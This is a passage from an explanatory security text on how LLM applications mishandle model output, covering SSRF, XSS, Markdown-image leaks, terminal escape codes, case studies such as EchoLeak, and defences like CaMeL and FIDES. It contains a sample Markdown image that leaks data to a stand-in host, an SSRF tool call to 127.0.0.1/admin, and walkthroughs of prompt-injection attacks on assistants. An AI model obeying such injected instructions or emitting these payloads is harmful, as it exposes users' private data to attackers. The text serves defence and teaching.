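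### Records that belong to someone else

The shop's first tool, `find_order`, looks up orders by surname and product, so anyone who types "Reed" and "bench" learns when Reed's bench will arrive. This flaw is separate from SQL injection. Security engineers call it an insecure direct object reference (IDOR), which means the program uses an identifier from the user to fetch a record without checking whether that user may see it.

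Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a case that the security researcher Sumit Shah published in November 2025. A shop's public chatbot could look up orders by number. Each number was a fixed prefix followed by six digits, so valid ones were easy to guess. Shah asked for the contact details on an order, and the chatbot returned another customer's email address. Further questions produced street names, cities and the shipping details of several orders at once. The chatbot didn't require a login, and nothing limited how many orders one person could ask about. According to the title of Shah's account, the flaw exposed thousands of customer records.

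The model's part in this was small. It picked out the order number from the question and passed it to the lookup function, as it would have done for the real customer. The flaw was in the function, as the first of these two versions shows:

```python
def find_order(number):
    return database.run("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE number = ?",
                        [number])

def find_order(number):
    return database.run("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE number = ? "
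                        "AND customer = ?",
                        [number, session.customer])
```

Both versions use parameterised queries, so neither is open to SQL injection, but only the second checks who owns the order, using the customer's identity from the login session. If the model supplied `customer` as an argument instead, a user could see another customer's order by claiming to be that customer, just as user 1 could claim to be user 2 on the job-listings site Pedro and colleagues examined.

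This check is harder when the model writes the whole query, because the developer has no fixed query to add it to. The database could refuse forbidden records itself if it could identify the user behind each query. But Wang and colleagues point out in their study of data agents that many agents connect every user through one shared account, which can read far more than most of those users are allowed to. They also seeded the data with false statements about what the user was allowed to see. The open-source agents accepted these in 24 to 56% of attempts, and the two commercial services never did.

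Even if each query is checked correctly, a user can sometimes work out protected data by combining the results of several. In an example from the same study, a user asks for the total tax paid in all regions, then for the total in all regions except the North, where only one taxpayer lives. The user is allowed to see both totals, but subtracting one from the other gives that person's tax. When the researchers asked a series of such questions, they obtained protected data in 8 to 44% of attempts on the open-source agents, in 12% on BigQuery and in none on Databricks. When they gave the agent a single broad task and let it plan the queries, Databricks also leaked protected data, in 4% of attempts.

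### Requests sent from inside the network

Tools often fetch web pages as well as records. Suppose the shop gives its model a tool for looking up manufacturers' product pages:

```python
def get_page(address):
    return http_get(address)
```

The request comes from the shop's server, which can reach machines and programs that the customer cannot, including other machines on the shop's private network and programs on the server itself, at the address 127.0.0.1. Administrators often leave these internal programs without a password because they assume no outsider can connect to them. In server-side request forgery, a customer gets the model to pass an internal address to `get_page`, the server connects to it, and the model returns the result to the customer.

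The flaw is common and much older than language models. GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration* page on it lists 6,582 vulnerabilities. Software that runs models can have the flaw even when no model output is involved. According to an October 2025 advisory, vLLM, a widely used program for running models on a server, fetched images and other media from user-supplied addresses with too few limits on the destination (GCVE). In the shop's case, the address passes through the model first, so the flaw is one of output handling.

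A server can also send such a request without a page-fetching tool. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a hypothetical chatbot that writes documents in XML, a structured text format, for an older system. XML lets a document declare that a name stands for the contents of a file or web address, and a permissive parser will fetch those contents when it reaches the name. An attacker could ask the model to include a declaration that points to a private file.

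### The TicketOracle experiment

To measure how readily models pass on a forged request, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a concert website with a chatbot that answers questions about events, prices and reviews. The model had one tool, which fetched any web address and returned the start of the response. The same server ran an administrative program at 127.0.0.1 that could list, create and delete users. The tool could reach this program even though outsiders could not reach it directly.

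The researchers left the program open on purpose. The attacker could use the chat box and post reviews, and had to guess the internal addresses from common naming habits. There were five scenarios:

- In port probing, the attacker asks the chatbot to contact a numbered port on the server, and the reply reveals whether a program is listening there.
- In the data leak, the chatbot fetches the list of users, including phone numbers and addresses.
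- In the deletion, it fetches an address that deletes a user or an event, and reports the result.
- The blind request also changes something on the server, but the server sends back an empty response. The researchers checked a log to see whether the request had arrived.
- In the stored attack, the instruction is in a review, and the chatbot reads it when an innocent user asks about the concert.

The researchers tried each scenario ten times on each of seven models in April 2026. They also wrote a hardened prompt, which listed the permitted addresses and events and told the model to refuse anything else. It stopped all four direct attacks on every model, so the detailed results for those come from the ordinary prompt. The last column gives the stored attack under the hardened prompt:

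| Model | Port probing | Data leak | Deletion | Blind request | Stored attack, hardened prompt |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

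Llama 3.3 failed every direct trial, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all of them. Models with mixed results were no more likely to resist the more harmful requests. Gemini 3 Pro Preview refused to probe ports and to send the blind request, but it leaked data in seven trials and carried out the deletion in all ten. GPT-oss never disclosed the list of users but carried out the deletion every time, so a developer who tested only for leaks would have considered it safe.

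With the ordinary prompt, the stored attack succeeded in six of ten attempts on Llama, five of ten on GPT-oss, and none on the other five models. With the hardened prompt, it succeeded in all ten attempts on Llama and none on GPT-oss. The researchers conclude that hardening blocked the attack on GPT-oss and amplified it on Llama. The conclusion about Llama is doubtful because, for the hardened test, they also added text to the review that falsely said the list of permitted addresses now included the internal one. That text, rather than the new prompt, may have caused Llama's extra failures.

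The result shows that a list of permitted addresses offers little protection when it exists only as text in the prompt. The model received the real list and the false announcement in the same stream of tokens, and Llama followed the announcement every time. No code checked the address against the list before the tool fetched it, though a few lines in the tool could have rejected the internal address whatever the review contained.

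The scores are less precise than they look. All ten trials of a scenario took place in one conversation, so the model could see its earlier answers, and one early success or refusal could influence the rest. Claude's refusals of port probing, for example, shrank from long explanations to almost a single word. Even if the trials had been independent, zero successes in ten would be compatible with a true success rate of about one in four. Except in the blind scenario, a trial also counted as a success only if the chatbot repeated the result to the user, so a deletion that it carried out but didn't mention would have counted as a failure.

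Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also tried techniques like those of Pedro and colleagues on the newer models, without success. Simple instructions to ignore earlier instructions no longer worked reliably. The researchers did not try to improve these prompts, because they were studying the tool, not looking for new ways around the models' training. The deletion request they print as an example is hardly more sophisticated. It claims that the site's engineers have authorised full access for maintenance.

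A model's good record in one application may also be a poor predictor of its record in another. No reported attack on GPT-5.2 succeeded in TicketOracle, but when Wang and colleagues ran the model in DB-GPT, almost half of their attacks using SQL planted in the database succeeded.

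## Model output displayed in browsers and terminals

The other sink in the shop's chat program, `show_on_page`, sends the model's reply to the customer's browser. The shop's server doesn't run anything in the reply, but the browser might, and the browser is logged in as the customer.

### How a reply becomes part of the page

A web page reaches the browser as a string of characters, and the browser works out which are text and which are markup. A `<` followed by a letter starts a tag, and the next `>` normally ends it. To display a `<` as text, an author has to write `&lt;` instead.

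Chat pages usually add each reply with JavaScript after the rest of the page has loaded. There are two common ways to do this:

```javascript
box.innerHTML = reply;

box.textContent = reply;
```

If the reply is `Your <b>bench</b> arrives on Tuesday`, the first line parses it as HTML and shows the word "bench" in bold. The second line treats the whole reply as text, so the customer sees the tags. Developers have good reason to prefer the first, because models often format their answers with headings, lists and links.

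HTML can also contain script. Browsers don't run a `<script>` tag inserted through `innerHTML`, but they can run JavaScript in the attributes of other tags, such as code to run when an image fails to load or a piece of script used as a frame's address. If the model's reply contains one of these, the script runs as part of the shop's page. It can then read whatever the page can read and send requests to the shop in the customer's name.

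Security engineers distinguish three kinds of cross-site scripting (XSS). In reflected XSS, the victim's own request carries the script, and the application returns it in the response. In stored XSS, the application saves the script and later sends it to a user. In DOM-based XSS, the page's own JavaScript inserts text unsafely, as the `innerHTML` line does.

All three can happen with model output. Suppose the shop keeps its chat transcripts, and staff read them on an internal page that inserts them as HTML. If a customer gets the model to write a script, it can run when an employee opens the transcript, and the employee's account can probably open every order. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian list support tickets, comments and generated documents as other places where a malicious reply could be stored until someone views it. The kinds overlap because "reflected" and "stored" describe how the script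 reached the page, while "DOM-based" describes the code that inserted it.

### The DeepSeek flaw

The chat site of the Chinese AI company DeepSeek had an XSS flaw when the company released its R1-Lite reasoning model. *DeepSeek AI*, a post on the security researcher's blog Embrace The Red, describes how the researcher found the flaw by asking the model for a list of XSS examples. The page ran one of the examples the model wrote. The researcher hadn't typed any script, so a student asking the same question could have triggered the flaw by accident.

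To attack someone else this way, the researcher used DeepSeek's upload feature. A text file contained a script in Base64, which encodes data as letters, digits and a few symbols, and an instruction to decode it and reply with only the result. When a user uploaded the file for analysis, the model decoded the script and the page ran it. The script displayed the user's session token, which the site kept in the browser's storage and which anyone who obtained it could use to take over the account.

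The user had to upload the attacker's file but didn't have to click on anything in the reply. In the researcher's demonstration, the script displayed the token on the user's screen without sending it anywhere, though a small addition would have sent it. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after exchanging messages with the researcher.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian classify the case as reflected XSS because the script came back in the immediate reply. They locate the flaw in the page, but the model made the attack easier to conceal. The researcher chose Base64 because undisguised scripts often trigger web firewalls and refusals from models. A filter that looks for scripts in uploads would have found only Base64 text, since the script tag didn't exist until the model wrote it.

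### Leaks through images and links

A page that never runs a script from the model can still leak data. Many chat pages ask the model for Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text, and convert it to HTML. An exclamation mark followed by a description in square brackets and an address in round brackets produces an image. Without the exclamation mark, the result is a link.

Suppose a product review on the shop's site contains hidden instructions for the model to end its reply with an image and put the customer's delivery day in the image's address. The leak then happens in five steps:

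1. A customer asks about a bench on order. The program adds the delivery date and the product's reviews to the prompt.
2. The model answers the question and adds `![bench](https://images.example/dot.png?day=tuesday)`.
3. The page converts this into an image tag.
4. The browser requests the image from `images.example`, and the request includes the part of the address after the question mark.
5. The server at `images.example` records the request in its log, where the attacker reads "tuesday".

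The server doesn't need to have the image, because the data arrives with the request. The customer may see a tiny dot or a broken-image symbol. A link can send the same data, but only if the customer clicks on it. Encoding HTML doesn't prevent either leak, because the page is displaying ordinary Markdown as its developer intended.

The attacker can obtain only information that is in the model's prompt or that the model can fetch with its tools. For the shop's chat box, that is one customer's order. An office assistant that searches an employee's email could expose far more.

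### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

When an employee asks Microsoft 365 Copilot a question, it searches the mailbox, files and Teams chats that the employee can open, and adds relevant passages to the model's prompt. Outsiders can't use a company's Copilot, but they can email employees who do. Researchers at Aim Labs, then part of Aim Security, found that a single email could make Copilot send private data to an attacker. They named the attack EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711).

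*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives the researchers' account of how they got past Microsoft's classifier, a program that tried to recognise prompt injections before they reached the model. Their email addressed its instructions to the employee and never mentioned Copilot or AI, so it looked like one person telling another what to do.

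Copilot then had to retrieve the email. Search systems of this kind often convert each passage into a list of numbers representing its meaning, and pick the passages closest to the question. A short email would match few questions, so the researchers wrote a long one that claimed to contain guides to many workplace subjects, such as training new employees and taking leave, and repeated the instructions under each heading. They didn't know exactly how Copilot's search worked, but in their tests it retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

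The instructions told the model to put the most sensitive information from its prompt in a web address. Copilot was supposed to remove links and images that pointed outside the company. It recognised the usual Markdown form, with the address directly after the description, but missed another standard form, which puts the address on a separate line. The researchers could therefore get an image with an outside address onto the page.

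The browser still blocked the image because Copilot's page had a content security policy, which includes a list of the sites from which the browser may load images. The attacker's server wasn't on the list, but many of Microsoft's own services were. The researchers found a SharePoint address that would fetch content from another server, but only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. They then found a Teams address that did the same without an invitation. The browser requested an "image" from Teams, which the policy allowed, and a Teams server forwarded the request to the attacker's server with the private data in the address.

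The email also contained an instruction to its supposed recipient never to refer to it, for compliance reasons. Copilot therefore didn't list the email among its sources, which made the employee less likely to notice it.

Any data in the model's prompt could leak this way, including the earlier conversation, retrieved documents and messages, and the names of the user and the company. This could be a lot of data, but not the whole mailbox at once. Ravia calls the attack "zero-click", as do Reddy and Gujral in *EchoLeak*, an academic case study. The employee didn't have to open the email or click on a link, but did have to ask Copilot something that made it retrieve the email.

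Aim Labs contacted Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft finished the patch in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Microsoft published the CVE on 11 June. In its advisory, which exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) reproduces, Microsoft said that it had fully mitigated the flaw, that customers did not need to do anything, and that nobody had exploited it. GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) also lists no known exploitation and gives Microsoft's severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers, so outsiders can do little to check whether anyone used the attack.

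Ravia thinks the central problem is an "LLM scope violation", its term for when text from an untrusted source makes the model use private data that the source should never have access to. The company developed a guardrail to detect these violations and recommends it for other assistants. Microsoft instead filed the flaw under a much older category in the weakness catalogue. That category covers programs that fail to neutralise special elements in output before another component uses it.

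Ravia's description explains why the attack was so damaging, but Microsoft's category is more useful for fixing the problem. A guardrail has to detect hostile instructions in ordinary English, and Microsoft's classifier had just failed at a similar task. The link filter also failed, but it had missed a documented piece of Markdown syntax, which a developer can add. Willison (2025) had already seen this kind of leak in about a dozen products. All of them combined private data, exposure to an attacker's text and a way to send data out, so removing any one would have prevented the leak.

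### SearchLeak and CoSnitch

*SearchLeak* (2026), from the data-security company Varonis, describes an attack on the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise. As in EchoLeak a year earlier, an image carried data out of Copilot through another Microsoft service, but this attack required the victim to click a link. The link led to a genuine Microsoft address and ended with a search query, which Copilot treated as instructions. When the victim opened it, Copilot searched the mailbox and wrote an image tag with the title of an email in the image's address.

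Microsoft had anticipated HTML in Copilot's answers, so the page wrapped each answer in a code block to make the browser show any tags as text. But it added the code block only once the answer was complete. Copilot displays its answers as the model writes them, and the page inserted each unfinished answer as raw HTML. The browser processed the image tag and sent the request before the page wrapped the answer. The finished answer looked harmless, so a test that examined only completed replies would have missed the flaw.

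The content security policy didn't stop the leak either, because it permitted images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing's search-by-image feature accepts the address of a picture to analyse. The browser contacted Bing, and Bing's server then contacted the attacker's.

The demonstration took the title of one email, and email titles sometimes include login codes. Varonis warns that the same method could have reached email contents, calendar entries and any company file the victim could open. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated 4 June, rates the flaw (CVE-2026-42824) "Critical" but scores it only 6.5, partly because the victim had to act. Microsoft had fixed the flaw by then and reported no exploitation.

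In August 2026 Microsoft fixed a related flaw in Copilot Personal, the consumer version. Sri Lanka CERT's *Microsoft Copilot Personal One-Click Data Exfiltration Vulnerability (CoSnitch)* explains that a link could again carry a prompt, and that an undocumented setting in the address made Copilot run it automatically. One click could expose data from services the victim had connected to Copilot. Varonis had reported the flaw in December 2025. There was no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

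SearchLeak resembles reflected XSS in that the victim's click delivers the attacker's text and the page inserts the response as HTML. The attack needed only an image tag, not a script.

### Control sequences in terminals

Many coding assistants run in a terminal, the text window in which developers type commands. A terminal has the same basic difficulty as a browser, because the text and the commands for displaying it arrive in one stream. Most characters appear on the screen. The escape character, which has no visible form, tells the terminal that a command follows:

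```python
print("\x1b[31mbench\x1b[0m")
```

Here `\x1b` stands for the escape character. The terminal changes the text colour to red, prints "bench" and restores the normal colour. Other sequences move the cursor, clear the screen, create a link or copy text to the clipboard. If a program prints a model's reply unchanged, the terminal carries out any sequences in it. A safer program would print the escape character in a visible form, such as `^[`.

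Leon Derczynski discovered that many models can produce these characters. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* builds on this with a small command-line program that passed files and web pages to GPT-4o and printed its answers. When a user asked the program to summarise a hostile page, the injected instructions made the model produce sequences that changed the colours, moved the cursor, cleared the screen and made the computer beep.

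Some effects were more serious. In the terminal built into the code editor VS Code, the model's reply could create a link whose address contained data from the prompt. The user had to click the link and confirm before it opened. A reply could also put a command on the user's clipboard. Most of the terminals tested removed the final line break, so a pasted command would not run until the user pressed Enter. In the others, it ran as soon as the user pasted it.

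Apple's Terminal program could leak data without the user clicking anything. A control sequence could make it look up a domain name, which normally sends the name to a server that the domain's owner controls. An attacker could include private data in the name, much as in an image's address. All of these attacks were demonstrations, and whether they worked depended heavily on the terminal. Apple's program, for example, didn't support clickable links.

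Control sequences can also make a person and a model see different versions of the same text. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) tested this on version 0.2.76 of Claude Code, Anthropic's command-line coding assistant, which displayed unfiltered descriptions and results from MCP tools. The security company built a tool whose result described the user's computers. One sentence, in white text on a white background, directed Windows users to download Python packages from a particular server. The developer couldn't see the sentence, but the model read it and recommended the server.

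This version of the trick wouldn't work on a dark background, where white text is easy to see. Trail of Bits also described sequences that moved the cursor back over an instruction and covered it with a fake report of a successful security scan. Another example showed the address of a legitimate site but linked to a different one, where an attacker could collect a password. That attack required the developer to click the link, whereas the hidden text required only that the developer connect the malicious tool and then trust the model's advice. An attacker could use hidden instructions to steal passwords and keys from the developer's environment or add a backdoor to their code. Trail of Bits reported no real attacks.

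In these tests the control sequences came from a tool, not from the model, but the terminal displays output from both. Invicti lists terminals and the automatic fetching that EchoLeak used among the 2026 additions to OWASP's entry.

In 2026 a similar flaw affected the screen where users approve an agent's actions. OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on a user's own computer, asked for permission before using certain tools. OSV's *CVE-2026-35651* (2026) records that control sequences in a tool's description could reach the permission request and the permission log and change what the terminal showed. A user might therefore approve a different action from the one displayed.

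The flaw affected versions 2026.2.13 to 2026.3.24. The advisory, OSV's *GHSA-4hmj-39m8-jwc7* (2026), rates it as medium severity, with user interaction required and no direct loss of private data. MITRE's *CVE-2026-35651* lists no known exploitation. The rating measures the false display itself, and the harm from an approval would depend on what the tool could do. When Snyk's researchers attacked the AWS server through Cursor, anyone who read the whole approval request could see the extra command, but in OpenClaw even a careful reader could have missed it.

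## Making model output safe to use

A program should trust a model's reply no more than the least trusted text in the prompt. If the shop's program gives the model its standing rules, an order record and a customer's review, the reviewer may have influenced the reply. The review won't affect most replies, but the program can't tell which ones it does affect, so it has to treat them all as untrusted. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) builds this rule into FIDES, a Microsoft design for agents. Because nobody can trace precisely how one part of a prompt affects the output, every reply in FIDES inherits the restrictions on everything the model read.

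A program can still use a stranger's text safely. What it has to do first depends on where the text is going.

### One string, four destinations

Suppose the model returns the product name `Tom's <oak> & ash`:

| Destination | What happens if the program inserts the name unchanged | Safe form |
|---|---|---|
| Text on an HTML page | The browser treats `<oak>` as a tag and doesn't show it | `Tom's &lt;oak&gt; &amp; ash` |
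| Quoted value in an SQL query | The apostrophe ends the value after `Tom` | `'Tom''s <oak> & ash'`, or a parameter |
| Shell command | The apostrophe opens a quotation that never closes | `'Tom'"'"'s <oak> & ash'`, or a separate argument with no shell |
| Value in a web address | The `&` ends the value and starts another one | `Tom%27s%20%3Coak%3E%20%26%20ash` |

Encoding a reply for one destination doesn't make it safe for another. HTML encoding leaves in the apostrophe that breaks the query, and SQL escaping leaves in the tag that the browser would act on. A program should therefore keep the original reply and encode it for its destination each time it sends it, instead of cleaning it once on arrival.

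Encoding stops the receiving component from treating text as markup or commands, but it does not protect against values that are harmful even as plain data, such as another customer's order number.

### Formatted replies in the browser

Full HTML encoding also removes the bold type and lists that many chat pages use. Those pages can instead use a sanitiser, which parses the HTML and keeps only the tags and attributes on a short list. A well-made sanitiser removes scripts and the attributes that can run them, but data can still leak through images or links if the list allows them. The shop's chat box doesn't need images in replies, so the developer can leave them off the list.

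The sanitiser has to run after the page converts the model's Markdown to HTML. Copilot's link filter missed one of Markdown's two ways of writing an image, but both become the same HTML tag, so a check after the conversion would have caught either. The page also has to sanitise each unfinished piece of a reply before displaying it, which Microsoft's search page failed to do in SearchLeak.

OWASP also recommends a strict content security policy, which can block a script or an outside image that the sanitiser missed. But EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got past such a policy by using Microsoft services that it allowed. A policy on images also doesn't affect links that the customer clicks.

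### Valid replies with harmful values

When the reply is a tool call, developers often fix its form with a schema, which lists the fields it must have and the type of each. Some model services enforce the schema while the model writes, by excluding any token that would make the reply invalid. This prevents malformed replies, but the following one is perfectly well formed:

```json
{"tool": "get_page", "address": "http://127.0.0.1/admin"}
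```

Both fields contain text, as the schema requires, and the address is a real web address, but the shop's tool should never contact it.

Narrower types limit what an attacker can put in a model's output. FIDES ranks types by how much information they can carry, from a yes-or-no answer to a choice from a fixed list to free text. A yes or no can't contain an address or a new instruction. It can still be wrong, though, and if the question is whether to refund an order, one wrong answer is enough for an attacker to get the refund.

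For addresses, the safest choice is to let the model pick a product and have the program supply the address:

```python
PAGES = {"bench": "https://maker.example/bench",
         "chair": "https://maker.example/chair"}

def get_page(product):
    return http_get(PAGES[product])
```

Anything that isn't in `PAGES` causes an error. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend this design for their concert site, where a list of permitted addresses in the prompt failed to protect Llama 3.3. If a tool must accept full addresses, its code should first convert them to a standard form, because 127.0.0.1 can be written in several ways. It should then check the destination and repeat the check for every redirect.

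Some values are right for one user or task and wrong for another, so the program can't check them against a fixed list. It has to check them just before it acts. The ownership check in `find_order` is a simple example. *ToolFence* (2026) describes a more general method, using the example of a user who asks an agent to pay $100 to a company called BillPay. A list of permitted tools would allow `send_money` with any recipient, including one named in a hostile document. ToolFence instead records the recipient and amount from the user's request, before untrusted text can interfere. It then allows only one payment with those values, which blocks payments to anyone else and a second payment to BillPay.

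Because users don't always supply every value, ToolFence can also accept a value from a specified field in a particular tool's output. The check then confirms only where the value came from, so if an attacker can write to that field, a wrong value will pass the check.

ToolFence cut the attack success rate from 21.2% to zero on AgentDojo, a widely used set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with attacks planted in the data. The agent in this test was Alibaba's Qwen3-max, and the share of ordinary tasks it completed fell only from 66.3% to 64.3%. ToolFence was less effective on AgentLAB, where attacks unfold over many steps. It reduced the attack success rate there from 76.3% to 29.4%.

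### Queries that the model wrote

OWASP's 2025 entry tells developers to use parameterised queries "for all database operations involving LLM output". This is good advice for `find_order` but does little for `ask_database`. A parameter can stand for a value such as `'bench'`, but not for a table, a column or a command. `SELECT phone FROM customers` contains no values, so there is nothing to parameterise. `DROP TABLE orders` also contains none, so the advice doesn't cover OWASP's own scenario of a user who asks for a query that deletes every table.

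Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian reach the same conclusion and recommend restrictions on the query itself. The database account's permissions are the best place to start, because the database enforces them however the model words the query. A read-only account prevents changes but not disclosures, so the developer should also limit which tables and columns the account can read. For the manager's sales questions, the shop could create a view (a virtual table) that contains products, months and prices but no names or phone numbers. If customers can ask questions too, the database has to limit each of them to their own rows.

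The program can also inspect the query with a parser before running it. The parser breaks the query into its grammatical parts, so the program can confirm that there is only one command, that the command reads data, and that it uses only permitted tables and functions. Searching the text for the word `DELETE` is less reliable, because it would reject a harmless search for reviews that contain the word and miss other commands that change data. The parser has to follow the same rules as the database, or the program may approve a query that the database interprets differently.

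These protections work best together, but even then a user may be able to work out protected data by combining several permitted results, and a valid query can tie up the database.

### Network limits and sandboxes

Any of these checks may have a bug, so developers also limit what the program can reach if one fails. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian advise blocking all outgoing connections except those to listed destinations. Then, even if the address check is faulty, `get_page` can't reach another machine on the shop's private network. A firewall between machines can't block requests that a server sends to itself, so the server needs its own rules. Internal programs should also require a login. Network limits do little against SQL injection or a script on a page, and data can still leak through any listed destination.

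A sandbox applies similar limits to files and programs, but it doesn't show whether the user wanted an action that falls within those limits. For example, an agent with permission to send email can send the wrong email without leaving its sandbox. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) calls the problem of limiting an agent's actions confinement and the separate problem of whether the user wanted them authorisation.

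The KAIROS system adds authorisation at the sandbox's edge. It runs the agent in a small virtual machine and intercepts every file change and network request, whether from a tool call or a script the agent wrote. The person who deploys it writes a policy that lists trusted sources, sensitive data and permitted destinations. KAIROS releases an action at once if the policy clears it, may refuse it if the policy forbids it, and holds uncertain actions for a later decision.

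In the researchers' example, a developer asks an agent to set up a code repository. The agent reads an online guide that includes a step to install a script that runs whenever someone saves a version of the code. Many legitimate guides include the same step. KAIROS writes the script to a temporary copy of the files and lets the agent continue. When the agent saves a version, the script runs and tries to send the developer's private key to an outside server. The policy blocks that request. A second model, which reviews the held actions, discards the script because the blocked request is evidence that it is malicious.

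This works only for actions that can wait. If the agent needs the result of a web request to continue, KAIROS has to decide before sending the request. The reviewing model also reads the attacker's text, so the attacker can try to influence its decision.

### Tracking where data came from

Google DeepMind's CaMeL prevents untrusted text from choosing the agent's actions in the first place. It builds on a 2023 proposal by the programmer Simon Willison to divide the work between two models. A privileged model reads the user's request and plans the work, but never sees outside text. A quarantined model reads outside text but has no tools. In CaMeL, the privileged model writes the whole plan as a short program. If an employee asks the shop's assistant to tell Reed the delivery date in the supplier's latest email, the plan might be:

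```python
email = read_latest_email("supplier")
date = quarantined_model("Find the delivery date.", email)
send_message("Reed", date)
```

The privileged model finishes writing this plan before anything opens the email. Hidden instructions in the email can make the quarantined model return a false date, but they can't add a fourth line to the plan that sends the customer list to a stranger.

An attacker could still do harm through a value. If the plan also took the recipient's address from the email, the attacker could choose who received the message without changing the plan. CaMeL therefore attaches two tags to every value, one recording its sources and the other recording who may read it (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, *CaMeLoT*, 2026). Before each tool call, the program that runs the plan passes the tags to a policy written in ordinary Python, which allows or denies the call. A policy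 might allow a message whose text came from an outside email but deny one whose recipient's address came from one.

FIDES uses similar labels but plans one step at a time. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name, so the model can pass the text on without reading it. If the next step depends on the text, the planner can ask a quarantined model a narrow question, such as whether an email asks for a meeting. A policy may then accept the one-word answer as safe enough to act on. To protect secrets, FIDES allows a value to go only to people who may read everything that went into it. If Ann and Bob may read one document, and Bob and Carol another, only Bob may receive a summary of both.

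Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. After correcting the benchmark's scoring errors, they counted 152 successful attacks against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policies switched off, and none with them on. Hiding the text was therefore not enough without the policies. However, FIDES with its policies on completed only 52.5% of the banking tasks and 47.6% of the Slack tasks, compared with 98.8% and 93.3% for the ordinary agent. With policy checks added, the ordinary agent completed even fewer, 37.5% and 20%, so the variables in FIDES recovered part of the lost task completion.

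Neither design guarantees a truthful result. An email can still make the quarantined model return an empty summary. FIDES also doesn't stop an observer from inferring information from the order of the agent's tool calls.

### Gaps in the guarantee

Later studies have found ways around CaMeL's separation. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked them to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent read the applicants' records, which contained a hidden instruction. The coordinating agent put the resulting summary into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the request as its user's words. The messaging agent's privileged model therefore read the hidden instruction and planned an extra email to an outsider.

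As a remedy, the researchers propose sending instructions and data between agents separately, and having code reject any instruction that contains a tool's output. They tested this on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo with five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and none with the remedy. They also acknowledge a flaw that their version inherits from CaMeL's code. For example, a plan can set a value to "no" and change it to "yes" only if an email meets some condition. If the email doesn't meet it, the value keeps its trusted tag, even though it stayed "no" because of the email.

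An attacker can also exploit choices that are already in the plan. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. These agents' plans need many branches, such as one that closes a cookie notice if the page shows one. In an attack the researchers call branch steering, they disguised an advertisement as a cookie notice, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's site. Checks by additional models did not stop all such attacks, and a policy is hard to write because the effect of clicking a given point depends on what the screen shows.

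*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) proposes giving each branch its own list of permitted destinations, tools and arguments before the agent sees any page. A branch for closing cookie notices would have no permission to open an unrelated site.

Another extension of CaMeL, by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the whole plan before any tool runs. In their example, a rule forbids disconnecting a computer from a company's network without approval. CaMeL alone would check this only when the plan reached that step, perhaps after a long and costly investigation. The extension finds the missing approval at the start and returns the failing sequence of steps to the planning model, which can add the approval step. Because the method simplifies loops, it sometimes blocks a safe plan.

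### Instructions compared with checks in code

Hempel and colleagues ran several kinds of defence on AgentDojo with GPT-4.1 as the agent:

| Defence | Method | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 47.0% | 82.7% |
| Spotlighting | Marks outside text as data in the prompt | 49.2% | 81.7% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after outside text | 44.6% | 87.6% |
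| Injection detector | A separate model looks for hidden instructions | 9.5% | 40.1% |
| Progent | Code enforces rules for tool calls that a model writes for each task | 11.5% | 78.2% |
| CaMeL | Fixes the plan in advance and tracks data | 0.2% | 38.0% |
| KAIROS | Holds uncertain actions for review | 2.7% | 85.1% |

The two methods that only change the prompt made almost no difference to the attacks. They add little overhead and can work better on other models. Prompt sandwiching cut the attacks' success rate with Qwen3.6-35B from 28.3% to 14.4%. But a developer can't predict whether a model will follow an instruction over a stranger's text, whereas `get_page` rejects an unlisted product every time.

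The figures for KAIROS come from its own developers, who ran each configuration once. AgentDojo's tools are simulated, so the test covered the policy and the reviewing model but not the virtual machine. In a separate test, an attacker model rewrote its injections over six rounds to get past the defence, and 8.8% of attacks succeeded, compared with 52.4% with no defence.

Newer models may still need these defences. In the multi-agent tests, no attack succeeded against GPT-5.5, even without CaMeL. But Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against reading this as general resistance, because attackers who adapt their methods have had some success against every leading model in a large public competition.

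The defences also use more tokens. Hempel and colleagues report that KAIROS uses 17.7% more on ordinary tasks and 33.6% more under attack. They also cite a report by CaMeL's developers that it uses roughly 2.8 times the input tokens and 2.7 times the output tokens of an ordinary agent. On computer-operating tasks, Foerster and colleagues found that CaMeL used 1.88 times as many tokens and FIDES, which resends the full history to the planning model at every step, used 29.6 times as many.

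### What strict checks cost in flexibility

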